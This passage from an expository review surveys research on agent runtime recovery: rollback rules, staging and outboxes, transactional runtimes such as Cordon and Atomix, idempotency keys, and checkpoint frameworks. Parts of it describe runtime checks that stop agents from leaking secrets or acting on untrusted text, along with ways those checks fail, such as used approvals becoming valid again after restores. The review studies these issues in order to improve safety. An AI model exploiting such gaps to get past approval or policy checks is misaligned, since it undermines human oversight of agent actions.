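The search writes the list of times and the invitation subtask reads it, so the two sets overlap. Since the invitations have gone out, DART blocks a rollback of the search alone.

Yang, Li and colleagues prove that some such rule is necessary. If a runtime undoes p without also rolling back, invalidating or compensating for a committed q, it can't guarantee a result equivalent to a correct run. The proof is short because it assumes that q's result depends on what p produced. The rule can also block harmless rollbacks, such as when the second search offers Tuesday again or the later step read a part of the data that didn't change.

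Refusing the rollback doesn't fix the invitations. A saga would cancel them and then redo the search. DART instead falls back on rerunning the whole task, which Yang, Li and colleagues describe as always safe but wasteful. Calling a rerun safe seems too generous in this example, because it could send everyone a second invitation while the first was still in their calendars.

### DART's results and limits

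The main tests covered navigation, filling in a schedule and diagnosing faults. Yang, Li and colleagues caused failures at chosen points, including some after the agent had committed work that recovery had to preserve. In one case, the agent had already submitted the schedule when the final display failed. The table shows the median number of actions repeated and the median recovery time for failures of this kind:

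| Task | Rerun everything | Restart the failed subtask | DART |
|---|---|---|---|
| Navigation | 18 actions, 25.8 seconds | Failed | 1 action, 2.5 seconds |
| Schedule | 29 actions, 34.7 seconds | Failed | 1 action, 1.1 seconds |
| Diagnosis | 16.5 actions, 21.2 seconds | Failed | 2 actions, 2.1 seconds |

DART and rerunning everything both succeeded every time in these tests. In a separate comparison of five models, DART recovered in only 80% of runs on one navigation case with a GPT model. A simpler method that restored an earlier, broader checkpoint also succeeded on navigation and diagnosis, repeating four and five actions respectively. For more ordinary failures, DART repeated as many actions as restarting the subtask did, so its advantage is mostly limited to failures that come after a commitment.

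The researchers also built a recovery program using the checkpoints of LangGraph, the agent toolkit. It failed in the schedule tests where the agent had already committed work, while DART succeeded after repeating one action. In the other three groups of tests, the LangGraph version succeeded and repeated no more actions than DART. Another demonstration tested the rule about committed steps on its own. Two finished steps had used the output of an earlier one, and DART did not allow a rollback of the earlier step. With the rule switched off, DART rolled it back and discarded both finished steps.

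Yang, Li and colleagues audited 47 recovery decisions across five kinds of task. DART allowed 35 rollbacks, none of which the audit found unsafe, and blocked 12 that would have been unsafe. This is encouraging, but even if the 35 were a random sample, seeing no failures would be compatible with a true failure rate of about 8%. The researchers wrote the audit's criteria themselves, and the criteria for navigation and scheduling didn't include a check for lasting outside effects, so the audit would be a poor way to find duplicate invitations.

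DART also depends on a person to review the boundaries, the data each subtask reads and writes, and the policy on side effects. A permitted move between states can be a bad boundary. In the schedule task, one such move would have marked a time slot as finished before the agent had settled it. If the reviewer forgets to record that the invitation subtask reads the list of times, DART detects no overlap and may allow the rollback it should block.

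Reviewing a small workflow may not take long. Each of the three main tasks had three kinds of subtask and ten boundaries to review. In the one timed session, one of the paper's authors, who had not built the original system, finished the schedule task's configuration in 27 minutes. An agent that plans its workflow as it runs has no fixed list of boundaries to review.

Finally, DART responds only to visible failures, such as an error message, a timeout, a missing input or a broken rule that the runtime checks. An outdated calendar can produce a list of times that looks normal. Unless something else compares that list with the current calendars, DART leaves the Tuesday invitations in place.

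## Holding effects back until the task is checked

In DART's example, if the runtime had held the Tuesday invitations until a check compared the list of times with the current calendars, fixing the mistake would have meant deleting unsent messages. Delaying an effect avoids the need to undo it, but the agent then has to continue without seeing the effect's results.

### The output commit problem

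Designers of fault-tolerant computer systems faced this trade-off long before language models. *A Survey of Rollback-Recovery Protocols in Message-Passing Systems* (Elnozahy, Alvisi and colleagues, 2002) describes groups of programs that save checkpoints so that they can resume after a crash. If one program goes back to a checkpoint, the others can go back too, so that none of them has received a message that the restored sender has not yet sent. Effects outside these programs can't be rolled back in the same way. For example, a printer can't undo a character it has printed.

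Before the system sends anything outside, it must therefore make sure it can recover the state that produced the output, whatever fails afterward. This is the *output commit problem*, which the survey credits to Strom and Yemini (1985). Suppose a bank's computer subtracts 100 from an account, tells a cash machine to pay out, and then crashes. If it restarts from a checkpoint saved before the withdrawal, the customer has both the cash and the original balance. The bank can save the new balance first, which delays the payout slightly, or pay at once and risk losing the money.

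*ACRFence* (2026), a paper on restoring agents from checkpoints, points out that agents have the same problem. Theirs is harder in one way, because an agent that misread the request or obeyed a planted instruction has to discard its work even if its state was saved perfectly. The bank's output was correct, and the only danger was that the computer would lose its record of it. An agent's runtime also has to wait for a check on the work itself, which may come minutes or hours later.

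### Private copies and outboxes

*Staging* an effect means holding it back, or applying it to a private copy, until commit. (The word has a different meaning in PocketOS's "staging environment".)

Private copies work well for files. *Fork, Explore, Commit* (Wang and Zheng, 2026) presents BranchFS, a file system that gives an agent its own *branch* of a directory. The branch starts empty. When the agent first changes a file, BranchFS copies that file into the branch and uses the copy from then on. If the agent deletes a file, BranchFS adds a marker that hides the original. A commit applies the deletions and changed files to the original directory, and an abort discards the branch.

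Creating a branch in BranchFS took about 0.3 milliseconds whether the directory held 100 files or 10,000. Committing a megabyte of changes took 2.1 milliseconds, and discarding it took 0.9. An agent can therefore try three repairs to a program in three branches and keep the first that passes the tests. BranchFS then invalidates the other two.

BranchFS prevents later writers from creating conflicting changes by making the original directory read-only while any branch exists. But a colleague who uses the same BranchFS directory can't save any work in it until the agent finishes.

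An agent working in a private copy can still send an email. Wang and Zheng note that aborting a branch doesn't reverse network requests, and that a complete system would also have to buffer outside actions. An *outbox* does this by storing the actions that the agent has requested and the runtime has not yet carried out. The runtime sends them on commit and deletes them on abort. *Beyond Memory* (2026) recommends saving each intended action along with the agent's own state and delivering it from an outbox afterward, so that the request survives a crash. A service can also hold actions itself, as Railway does by waiting 48 hours before deleting volumes.

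### Cordon's transactions

Cordon, the runtime that Chen and colleagues presented in June 2026 with the outage example, uses both devices. It treats a whole task as one *semantic transaction*, which goes through three phases:

1. **Prepare.** The agent works as usual, but file changes go to a private copy, which Cordon calls shadow state, and outside actions go to an outbox. Cordon also records which results influenced which later actions.
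2. **Validate.** Cordon checks the recorded influences, the file changes and the waiting actions together.
3. **Commit or abort.** If the checks pass, Cordon applies the file changes and releases the approved actions. Otherwise it discards the changes and cancels the actions.

In the outage task, the note on how to fix the failures would sit in shadow state and the Slack message in the outbox. Validation would then find the path from the log through the summary to the message, and Cordon would hold the message if the channel wasn't cleared for secrets from that log.

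Chen and colleagues write the main commit condition as

commit(T) ⇒ valid(T, C_t) ∧ staged(E) ∧ recoverable(W, D).

A transaction T may commit only if it is valid under the constraints C_t, all its outside effects E are still waiting, and Cordon can still reverse its local writes W and deletions D. C_t covers what the user wants, what the agent may do and what the policy permits at time *t*, so a user who changes their mind before commit can still stop the action. For T to be valid:

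- No secret, or text derived from one, may reach an unauthorized destination.
- Untrusted text may not lead to a sensitive file change unless the policy allows it.
- The record must include every operation that has a side effect.
- A person's approval must cover one action on one object, sent to one destination within a limited time.

This design helps with commands whose effects a checker can't predict. Cordon runs a command in a copy of the workspace, with network access off by default, then checks which files changed. In one test, a routine-looking setup command added data to the settings for SSH, a program for logging in to other computers. A rule based on the command's name or arguments would have had little evidence of this change, but Cordon found it in the copy and blocked it. In another test, a clean-up command stayed inside its permitted folder but would have deleted more files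 than the policy allowed. EffectMatch, the system in *Beyond Approved Actions*, similarly collects an operation's actual changes before they are committed and compares them with what the user approved.

Cordon is weaker at holding back network requests. If a tool needs network access, Cordon lets the command contact approved addresses through a proxy and records the traffic. These requests seem to go out before validation, so the outbox holds only the actions the agent requests as separate tool calls.

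Cordon's own crashes need rules too, because a crash halfway through a commit could leave some changes applied and others not:

| When Cordon crashed | What it does on restarting |
|---|---|
| After preparation, with no record that anything ran | Aborts |
| While commands were running | Asks a person to review, because it can't tell how far they got |
| During validation | Validates again |
| After validation, before the commit finished | Compares the files with a saved list of planned changes, then finishes if they are consistent and rolls back if not |
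| After sending an outside action | Doesn't resend it without evidence that the first attempt failed |

### Cordon's test results

Chen and colleagues wrote 45 workflows that each led to an action their policy forbids. An agent with no defense carried out the forbidden action in all 45. Programs that imitated existing kinds of defense stopped it in 14 cases, detected it too late in 5 and missed it in 26. Cordon stopped it before commit in all 45.

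This is good evidence that Cordon's checks work as designed, but weak evidence of how far it outperforms other products. The researchers built the workflows around the risks that Cordon's conditions describe, and they tested small adapters that imitate where each defense sits, not full rival systems. The 45 cases pair nine kinds of defense with five kinds of risk, so each adapter faced only five cases. The total of 14 doesn't show how many cases a company would stop by using several defenses together.

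Cordon also preserved performance on ordinary tasks. Agents completed 90.0% of a set of customer service tasks with Cordon and 87.5% without it, and they completed 100% of a set of command-line tasks in both cases. Chen and colleagues report only correctness for these tasks, so it is unclear how often Cordon would interrupt harmless work for approval.

The rollback tests used five scripted failures, with three trials each and no language model. After each rollback, a program checked whether the task could continue:

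| Method | Median rollback time | Median time including the failed step and the check | Median leftover file differences | Trials that could continue |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Cordon | 4.2 ms | 179 ms | 0 | 15 of 15 |
| Git restore | 11.0 ms | 100 ms | 73 | 0 of 15 |
| Git reset | 12.3 ms | 100 ms | 73 | 0 of 15 |
| Git reset and clean | 21.7 ms | 111 ms | 0 | 12 of 15 |

Git's restore and reset commands left behind new files that Git wasn't tracking. Adding a clean-up command removed those files, but the task still couldn't continue when the agent had changed file permissions. Cordon's rollback step is fast because Cordon does most of the work beforehand. That preparation makes its total time the longest, but a tenth of a second is an acceptable delay for a rollback that works.

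Excluding time spent waiting for approval, Cordon reduced the mean time for the 45 risky workflows by 25% to 28%. When that wait is included, runs took 23% longer if the tester approved every request and 7.5% less time if the tester rejected every request. The 23% increase implies a wait of only 12 or 13 seconds per task, and a real person may take much longer to respond. Chen and colleagues attribute the savings to stopping unsafe runs early, but that can't be the whole explanation, because the agent used the fewest tokens when every request was approved.

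### Atomix and the travel booking

Cordon holds back every outside action it can, which would make it hard to book a trip, because an agent needs to know whether the hotel has a room before it reserves a car. *Atomix* (Mohammadi, Potamitis and colleagues, 2026) treats actions differently according to whether they can be reversed. In the paper's example, an agent reserves a flight, a hotel and a car and then emails a confirmation.

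A small program called an *adapter* wraps each tool and labels its effects. The adapters label the three reservations as reversible, so Atomix makes them immediately and the agent receives the real confirmation numbers. The email is irreversible, so its adapter holds it and reports it to the agent as queued. If the flight booking fails, Atomix cancels the completed reservations, as a saga would, and deletes the queued email. A third label covers changes that Atomix can postpone, such as writing a local file.

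Atomix needs a signal that the agent has finished, or it might send the confirmation before the agent has tried to book the car. The *orchestrator*, the part of the runtime that schedules the work, therefore *seals* the transaction once all its calls have ended. Sealing fixes the list of everything the transaction has read and everything it will change. If a tool later tries to add to this list, Atomix aborts the transaction.

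Other agents may be working on the same trip, so Atomix also has to settle their changes in order. Each transaction gets a number called an *epoch*, and later transactions get higher numbers. Each resource *r*, such as the hotel booking, has a *frontier*. The orchestrator may raise the frontier to *e* only when every transaction that uses *r* and has an epoch below *e* has committed or aborted. A sealed transaction T may commit only when

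frontier(r) ≥ e(T)

for every resource *r* that T has read or will change. Here e(T) is the highest epoch among T's recorded reads and effects.

Suppose transaction A has epoch 5 and is moving the hotel booking to another date. Transaction B has epoch 7. It has read the booking and wants to email the itinerary, and it is ready first:

| Moment | frontier(hotel) | frontier(mailbox) | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
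| B is sealed while A is still working | 5 | 7 | B waits, because 5 < 7 |
| A is sealed | 5 | 7 | A commits, because 5 ≥ 5 |
| A has finished | 7 | 7 | B satisfies the rule |

B's email still contains the old date, so Atomix needs another check. It keeps a version number for each resource and records that number when a transaction reads the resource. If A's change raised the hotel booking from version 3 to version 4, Atomix aborts B, deletes its email and schedules a retry. A transaction that involves only an unrelated car rental has its own frontier and never waits for transactions on the hotel booking.

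These rules ensure that a transaction is complete and based on current data, but not that it is sensible. When Mohammadi and colleagues gave Atomix 22 transactions with invalid content, it committed all 22. After they added a program that checks the content before commit, it committed none. Without such a program, Atomix would release the outage agent's Slack message with the key in it.

### Atomix's test results

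In their main recovery test, Mohammadi and colleagues ran a GPT-4.1 agent on retail tasks from τ-bench, the predecessor of τ²-bench. They made tool calls fail at random and counted a task as a clean success only if the agent completed it without leaving duplicates, unwanted changes or failed cancellations.

With a 30% chance of a fault at each call, Atomix had a clean success in 17 of 30 tasks (57%). *Checkpoint replay*, which restores the workflow's saved state and runs it again, had 16 (53%). The two are statistically tied, as they were in a larger test with fewer faults. The six other methods scored between 0% and 7%. These were all versions that the researchers wrote for the experiment, not finished products.

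The size of Atomix's lead over the weaker methods depends on how faults arrive. With independent faults at a rate of 10%, Atomix scored 73% and an agent without a transaction system scored 27%. When faults came in bursts, at an overall rate of about 12%, the scores were 67% and 60%. Real outages often come in bursts, so developers may see results closer to the second comparison.

The email test separates Atomix from checkpoint replay. The agent prepared an email, and then something made the email invalid, such as a failed tool or outdated information. There were five such causes, with 100 trials of each:

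| Method | Invalid emails sent, out of 500 |
|---|---|
| Atomix | 0 |
| Try-confirm-cancel | 0 |
| Locks, a log and rollback | 0 |
| Checkpoint replay | 200 |
| Saga | 400 |
| No transaction system | 500 |
| Atomix with the email tool mislabeled | 300 |

Atomix and all the methods compared with it sent all 500 emails in a matching set of valid cases, so Atomix didn't reach zero by blocking everything. Two other methods also reached zero: *try-confirm-cancel*, which makes a provisional request and later confirms or cancels it, and a method that combines locks with a log of changes. They needed about 50 and 30 lines of code respectively for the email tool, compared with 17 for an Atomix adapter. The test is therefore strong evidence for holding emails back, but much weaker evidence that Atomix is the best way to do it.

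### Restoring the agent along with its files

After an abort, the agent's context still describes files that the runtime has just discarded. Zhuang, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *AgentRewind*, address this by saving the two together. Each time the model makes a decision, AgentRewind records a checkpoint

d_t = (c_t, s_t),

where c_t is the agent's context and s_t is the state of the files in its workspace. An agent that gets stuck can choose an earlier checkpoint and write a note about what went wrong. AgentRewind restores the context and the files and adds the note to the context, so that the agent doesn't repeat the mistake.

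In one test, agents had to repair an astronomy library and then catalog its image files, including six deliberately broken ones that had to stay unchanged. One agent ran the catalog program in the wrong mode, which overwrote the broken files, and couldn't recreate their exact contents. Another kept restarting from the beginning, which recovered the files but discarded its finished repairs, and it failed after 26 restarts. The agent with AgentRewind also chose the wrong mode, but it went back to just before that command, kept its repairs, and passed all ten checks.

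Across 82 engineering tasks with GPT-5.4, AgentRewind raised the success rate from 62.2% to 87.8%. Zhuang and colleagues also removed one part at a time:

| Version | Tasks completed |
|---|---|
| No rewinding | 62.2% |
| AgentRewind | 87.8% |
| Without restoring the files | 43.9% |
| Without restoring the context | 65.9% |
| Without the note | 51.2% |

An agent whose context was rewound without restoring its files did worse than one that never rewound, probably because its context no longer matched the files on disk.

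The benchmark probably favors rewinding. Zhuang and colleagues built it from tasks in which ordinary commands destroy information, and the agent was told the first unmet requirement after each failed submission. They did confirm that every task can be solved without rewinding. The gain was smaller on Terminal-Bench 2.0, an existing benchmark, from 78.7% to 83.1%.

AgentRewind restores only the files in the workspace, not running programs. *DeltaBox* (2026) warns that a program's memory and its files no longer match if a rollback covers only the files. AgentRewind also can't unsend an email. If the agent sent one after the checkpoint, the restored context won't mention it unless the agent put it in the note. If it didn't, the agent is in the same position as the bank's computer after the crash, with no record of a payout that the customer has already received. An outbox would prevent this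 by holding the email until a rewind was no longer needed.

### What the delay costs

An agent sometimes needs the real reply to an action before it can choose the next one. Trofimov and Novikov (2026), in *When Tool Calls Succeed but Workflows Fail*, give the example of an agent that negotiates for its user. The agent can't learn how the other side will react to an offer without sending it, and a "queued" message contains no information about that reaction.

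Some services avoid this problem by offering price quotes or holds that expire by themselves. In another of Trofimov and Novikov's examples, an agent with a budget of 1,500 euros books a 900-euro flight and a 700-euro hotel at the same time. Both bookings succeed, the total is over budget, and the flight is nonrefundable. If the agent had first asked for quotes, the runtime could have added them up before the agent bought anything. If the agent had placed a hold instead, it could have let the hold lapse.

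Running reversible actions immediately, as Atomix does, gives the agent real replies, but it also exposes the actions to other people before commit, as in a saga. *AtomicFaaS* (2026) notes that compensation in general has this weakness. A supplier may start work on an order that the agent then cancels, and the supplier can't recover the time spent.

A held action may be out of date by the time the runtime releases it. *Boundary-State Control for Tool-Using Language-Model Agents* (2026) proposes measuring how often a system commits actions that have become invalid and, separately, how often it commits actions that are still valid. Both measures are necessary because a system that refused every action would score perfectly on the first.

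Checking version numbers detects such changes but also flags harmless ones. *Stale Does Not Mean Unsafe* (Zheng, Long and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent about to put a copy of a dataset into use. A failed quality check and a routine audit update both change the copy's version number, but only the failed check makes it unsafe to use. Atomix's version check has the same weakness. If someone corrected a spelling mistake in the hotel booking, Atomix could abort a transaction that had read the booking, cancel that transaction's own reservations and make them again, possibly with a cancellation fee.

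All these decisions depend on correct labels. Besides the mislabeled email tool, Mohammadi and colleagues tested adapters that listed too few of the resources a call affects, and conflicting changes got through in 66 of 200 trials. Listing too many resources caused no such errors and only made transactions wait for each other more often, so a developer who is unsure is safer listing too many than too few.

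The Model Context Protocol gives developers little help with labeling because it has no hint for whether a tool supports holds, staging or a separate commit step. Trofimov and Novikov collected the descriptions of 98,291 tools in July 2026 and found that only 12.9% had a destructiveness label that applied to them. The rest either had no such label or were marked read-only, which makes the label irrelevant. So someone has to work out by hand how to treat most tools that change something.

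Finally, when an outbox contains several actions, the runtime may complete only some of them. Suppose it holds a bank transfer and an email telling the recipient that the money is on its way. The runtime has to send one first, and the second may then fail permanently. Both Mohammadi et al. and Trofimov and Novikov agree that no runtime can prevent this on its own. The bank and the mail service would both have to support a *prepare* step, in which each guarantees that it can carry out its action, and then a *commit* step, in which both do so. Ordinary mail servers and most web services don't support this.

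Atomix retries the failed action a limited number of times, then stops and reports which actions went out. A developer can also order the actions to make a partial failure less serious. For example, if the transfer goes first and the email fails, the recipient gets money without a notice, which is easier to fix than a notice without money.

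## Repeated effects after retries and restored checkpoints

Retrying a failed action, as Atomix does, is safe only if the first attempt had no effect, and the sender often can't tell whether it did. Suppose an agent calls `send_money("BillPay", 100)`. The payment service moves the money and replies, but the network loses the reply (a *lost acknowledgment*), so the runtime reports a timeout. If the agent treats the timeout as a failure and pays again, BillPay receives $200.

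A timeout can also mean that the request never arrived, or that the service is still working on it. The agent should pay again only if the request never arrived, but it gets the same timeout in all three cases. A refund would compensate for the duplicate, but the user would be short $100 until it came through.

### Idempotency keys

An *idempotency key* is an identifier that the caller sends with a request so that the server carries out repeated copies only once. For the BillPay payment, it works like this:

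1. The runtime creates a key, such as `pay-7f21`, and saves it before the first attempt.
2. It sends the key with the payment. The service stores the key along with the payment's result.
3. If no reply arrives, the runtime sends the same request again with the same key.
4. The service finds the key in its records and returns the stored result without moving any money.

Liu, Liu and Lu (2026), in *RetryBench*, worked out what a retry does in each case. Applied to the payment, their table gives the total number of payments BillPay receives:

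| What happened to the first request | Retry with the same key | Retry with a different key |
|---|---|---|
| It failed before doing anything | 1 | 1 |
| It is still in progress and will finish later | 1 | 2 |
| It finished, but the reply was lost | 1 | 2 |

The key protects against repeated effects only while the service keeps it, which is 24 hours under the rules of Liu and colleagues' tests. An agent that resumes after that could send the right key and still pay twice.

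### Checking before a retry

Without a key, an agent can check recent payments before it retries. In *Where Does Exactly-Once Live?*, Li (2026) tested this approach with nine models on simulated services for billing, email, deployment and similar jobs. Each task included an instruction to perform every action exactly once. After a lost acknowledgment, the six strongest models duplicated the action in only 0.5% of runs, because they nearly always checked first. When the original request was still in progress, they did so in 56% of runs, because they checked, found nothing and retried, and then the original request went through.

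Li proves that checking can't solve this by itself. Suppose an agent always completes the payment within time T when the first request has disappeared for good. To do that, it must send the payment again by time T. Now suppose the first request is only delayed, and that it finishes after

δ > T + λ,

where λ is the time a finished payment takes to appear in the list. Until the agent retries, it sees exactly what it would see if the request had disappeared. It therefore retries here too, and both payments go through.

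Waiting helps if the service guarantees a maximum processing time. When every delayed request took 90 seconds, a rule that waited at least two minutes before checking gave the right result in 99% of runs. When delays ranged from 40 seconds to two hours, even waiting an hour succeeded in only 84% of runs. With the same delays, when every service accepted keys, agents succeeded in 92% of runs and took about a minute of simulated time.

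Across a wider set of faults, adding keys to every service cut the duplicate rate from 28% to 4%. When agents retried a delayed request with its original key, none of the 432 retries caused a duplicate. The remaining duplicates came from agents that had sent no key the first time or changed it for the retry.

Agents duplicated actions more often when the service offered a list to check (about 30% of runs) than when it didn't (13%), because without a list they usually asked a human operator. The simulated operator could see what had really happened, so real operators would probably help less. Users may not notice the duplicates, since agents reported the task as complete in 90% of the runs that contained one.

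### Who should write the key

A model that writes or copies the key can get it wrong. Liu and colleagues gave models a timed-out call, its valid key and a clear statement of the service's rules. OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Luna reused the valid key in all 40 trials when the prompt showed no other key. When the prompt also showed an invalid key labeled "Candidate recovery key", Luna reused the valid one in only 10 of 40 trials. With the invalid key relabeled "Alternative key string", it reused the valid one in 39. Two sibling models, Sol and Terra, reused the valid key every time. The tests covered only four software tasks, so they are weak evidence of how often this happens in practice, but there is no good reason to leave the choice to the model.

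The runtime can compute the key instead. *Verified Tool Calls Improve LLM Agent Reliability Under Non-Atomic Failures* (2026) uses

k = hash(agent, action type, payload, time window),

so an identical call in the same time window always gets the same key. This has two drawbacks. If the user really wants two identical payments within the window, the service will ignore the second. And if the model rewords the payment note before retrying, or the retry falls into the next window, the key changes and the protection is gone. Li suggests fixing one key for each intended action and replacing whatever key the model supplies on a retry. This seems better, provided the runtime can tell which calls belong to the same intended action.

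No key helps if the server ignores it. The runtime can then only check before retrying, which leaves the gap that Li describes.

### UndoBench's paired runs

Sah, Sah and colleagues (2026), in *UndoBench*, measured how much this matters across different services. They ran each task twice from the same starting state and random seed, once normally and once with a lost acknowledgment. An agent that fails both runs may simply be unable to do the task. They therefore measured recovery only among pairs where the normal run succeeded:

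recovery rate = P(success with the fault | success without it).

The main study used 12 tasks and two small models, Llama 3.1 8B and Llama 3.2 3B, for a total of 2,880 pairs. Agents succeeded in 83.5% of the normal runs. Of those 2,406 successes, only 1,124 (46.7%) had a matching success when the acknowledgment was lost. The study compared three ways of handling the error:

| Method | Recovery rate | Trials with a duplicate effect |
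|---|---|---|
| Naive retry (up to three more attempts) | 42.8% | 53.3% |
| Retry with idempotency keys | 53.5% | 45.4% |
| Retry with a local log of calls | 43.9% | 51.7% |

The local log barely helped because it recorded what the agent had sent, not what the service had done.

The keys improved the average only slightly because only three of the 12 tasks used a service that supported them. With keys, every competent run on those three tasks recovered. Three other tasks were safe for other reasons. For example, Git rejects an attempt to create the same release tag twice. The remaining six had no protection, and in five of them every trial with keys still produced a duplicate.

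The overall gain of 10.7 percentage points had a 95% confidence interval of 0 to 24 points and was far from significant after correction for multiple comparisons. Repeating each task with 20 seeds doesn't help much, because the uncertainty comes from having only 12 tasks. The results for individual tasks are more useful. Runs with keys had 86 additional recoveries, including 48 in subscription renewals and 28 in wire transfers. The other 10 were in a database migration that a uniqueness rule already protected, so the keys may not have caused them. The average gain therefore depends mostly on how many of the chosen services honor keys.

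Later tests with Gemini 3.8 Flash and GLM-5.2 support this reading. These newer models completed 79.2% of normal runs, but their recovery rate was only 21.5% with naive retry and 33.2% with keys. The difference between the two recovery rates narrowly missed significance after correction. When Sah and colleagues made all 12 services honor keys, recovery rose to 97.2% and there were no duplicates. The 21 remaining failures came from empty or malformed model output, which keys cannot fix.

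The naive method resends calls automatically after any error, so the 53.3% figure does not measure how often a model would choose to pay twice. Li also found that retries made by the runtime without telling the model cut the share of runs with no missing or repeated effects from 72% to 50%, because the duplicate existed before the model could check anything. Developers should turn off automatic retries for calls that change something, unless the service honors idempotency keys.

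Keys also can't repair a half-finished job. Sah and colleagues interrupted the service partway through four tasks with several internal steps. Neither naive retry nor ordinary keys recovered any runs. Checking first recovered 25.9% of runs, all in one cloud deployment task where the agent could see which part had finished and had a tool to do the rest.

### A restored agent writes a new key

Restoring a checkpoint can repeat a payment even when no reply goes missing. If the agent crashes after paying and the runtime restores a checkpoint from before the payment, the model has no record of the payment and pays again. If the model generates the idempotency key, it will probably generate a new one for the second request, and the bank will treat the two requests as separate payments.

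*ACRFence* tested this with Claude Code, running the model Qwen3-32B, and a simulated bank that rejected repeated reference numbers. The agent made a duplicate transfer in all 10 trials with a restore and in none of 10 without one. Ten trials of one setup can't show how common the problem is, but the comparison is good evidence that the restore causes it. The bank's duplicate detection worked as designed, but it only catches retries that reuse the original reference number. An ordinary program usually does this when it retries, but a language model can't be relied on to. Even with random sampling turned off, small rounding differences in the hardware can change a model's output.

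The proposed remedy is a program that sits between the agent and its tools and logs every irreversible call. After a restore, a second model compares each new call with the log, ignoring details that naturally vary, such as reference numbers. If the call matches an earlier one, the program returns the recorded result without repeating the action. If the amount or recipient differs, the program blocks the call until someone explicitly starts a new branch of the run. The researchers did not build or evaluate this system.

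Comparing the calls is the difficult part, because a second transfer of $500 to Bob may be an accidental repeat or a payment that the user wants, and the two can look identical. The model that compares them can also make mistakes, or an attacker can mislead it. A fixed workflow avoids much of this guesswork, because the runtime can tie the key to a named step, such as "May rent", and store the key outside the checkpoint. An agent that plans as it goes has no predefined steps to tie keys to.

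Even with an outbox, a runtime that crashes after sending an action but before marking it as sent must either repeat the action or risk losing it.

### Six properties of a safe resume

Many developers get checkpoints from a *framework*, a ready-made set of tools for building agents. Khan (2026), in *Resume Means Resume*, asks what a framework should guarantee when a run stops and continues, and lists six properties:

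1. **Prefix continuation:** The run continues from the last saved point, with the state it had there.
2. **Effect exactly-once:** A completed effect, such as a payment, doesn't happen again on the same branch of the run.
3. **Fork determinism:** If someone deliberately goes back and answers an approval request differently, the new branch follows the new answer.
4. **Checkpoint validity:** The framework refuses to save a state that breaks its own data rules.
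5. **Consume-once:** At most one resume can use a given approval, and delivering the same answer again has no effect.
6. **Recovery determinism:** Two recoveries from identical saved records make the same decisions about what to skip and what to redo.

Fork determinism and consume-once can conflict. Suppose the answer "yes" arrives twice for the same approval. The second copy may be an accidental repeat, which the framework should ignore, or a deliberate request for a second branch, which it should carry out. Khan proves that no framework can handle both correctly unless the request contains something that distinguishes them.

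Khan also wrote a mathematical model of a well-behaved framework and gave a machine-checked proof that it satisfies all six properties for any number of steps and crashes. The proof shows that the properties are compatible when requests carry the necessary marker, but not that any real framework has them. To check real frameworks, Khan tested specific versions of five in July 2026. Most tests used ordinary programs in place of a language model, so a model's mistakes couldn't affect those results. Khan counted the effects in a separate record outside the framework.

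| Framework | Completed work after a resume | Other results |
|---|---|---|
| LangGraph 1.2.9 | Not repeated after a pause for approval, but repeated after a crash | Ignored a changed answer and silently saved invalid data |
| LlamaIndex Workflows 2.22.2 | Not repeated with one recommended pattern, but repeated with another, as the documentation warns | Followed a changed answer and rejected invalid data |
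| CrewAI 1.15.2 | Repeated, although the checkpoint documentation says otherwise | Not tested on approvals |
| pydantic-graph 1.107.1 | Not repeated | Couldn't resume at all after a crash in the middle of a step |
| AutoGen AgentChat 0.7.5 | Not repeated | Rejected corrupted data, but had no approval mechanism to test |

After a crash and a restore from a checkpoint, CrewAI rebuilt its own counter from the beginning, so the counter had the correct value, but the separate record showed that the first step had run twice. If that step had charged a card, the customer would have paid twice, and nothing in the agent's saved state would have revealed it.

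LangGraph's handling of changed answers could also hurt someone. When a person returned to a saved approval request and answered "no" instead of "yes", LangGraph used the earlier "yes". This happened in all 80 of Khan's runs with two Claude models, because the fault is in how the framework chooses which answer to use.

These tests covered particular versions and particular paths, and they don't show how often the faults occur in practice. The developers may since have fixed some of the faults. DBOS, an alternative that records each step of a program in a database, passed every test Khan gave it, but took 2.9 to 5 times as long as LangGraph to act on an approval.

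### One approval used by several processes

LangGraph ignored a repeated approval if it arrived after the run had finished. But the approved action happened more than once when several processes shared a database and resumed the same paused run at about the same time. This might happen if a company runs several copies of its server and a message reaches more than one of them. With two processes, the action happened twice in all 10 repetitions of the test. With 16, it happened 16 times from a single approval, again in every repetition.

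LangGraph doesn't permanently record an approval as used until the approved step has finished. Any process that checks the approval before then will read it as unused. A slow step, such as one that waits for a model's reply, leaves more time for this to happen.

Khan's first repair checked for a conflict when a process recorded the approval, but it detected the second process only after that process had carried out the action. The working repair makes each process claim the approval in the shared database before the step begins. The database accepts one claim and rejects the others. The action then happened exactly once in each of 10 repetitions on each of two databases, and also when the processes ran on separate machines. The repair is optional because LangGraph uses the same operation to inspect and resume a paused run, so inspecting a run could use up its approval unless the caller marks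 the request as an inspection.

### Approvals that return with old state

Restoring an agent can also restore permission it has already used. Suppose a manager approves one deletion and the agent carries it out. If the runtime then restores a checkpoint saved after the approval but before the deletion, the agent again holds an approval that looks unused, because the restored state has no record of the deletion.

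Whether a used approval works again after a restore depends on where the system records its use. If the record is part of the restored state, the restore erases it. If the service only checks that an approval is genuine, it has no record of use. In *ACRFence*'s small test, a service of this kind accepted a used approval both times, while a service that kept its own list of used approvals rejected every attempt. The system must therefore keep the record where restoring the agent doesn't affect it.

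This applies to several designs that limit an agent's permissions. ToolFence, for example, keeps the number of remaining uses in a database. If an operator restored that database along with the agent, the used permissions would become available again. *ACRFence* cites a report of a similar problem in HashiCorp Vault, a program for storing secrets, where a single-use token reappeared after someone restored a saved copy. An expiry time limits the damage because restoring an agent doesn't reset the clock on the service that checks the approval.

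Single-use tokens alone don't prevent repeated effects, because an agent that replans or retries may ask for a new token, and the system may issue one for an approval that the agent has already used. *Beyond Single-Use Tokens* (Xu, Fan et al., 2026) shows that to prevent this, the issuer must keep a permanent record of the action, the person's confirmation and the number of uses left, which can only go down. The paper's system and a plain server-side ledger with the same information both prevented repeated authorization, so the record seems to matter more than the form of the token.

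If the system marks the approval as used and then crashes before acting, the agent has to ask again. If it acts first and then crashes, the approval may work a second time. For an irreversible action, marking first is usually safer, because a second approval prompt does less harm than a second deletion. If the service supports idempotency keys, the runtime can avoid this choice by using the approval's identifier as the key, so that a repeated request returns the original result. Xu and colleagues likewise found that their record prevented duplicate effects only when the receiver ignored repeated requests.

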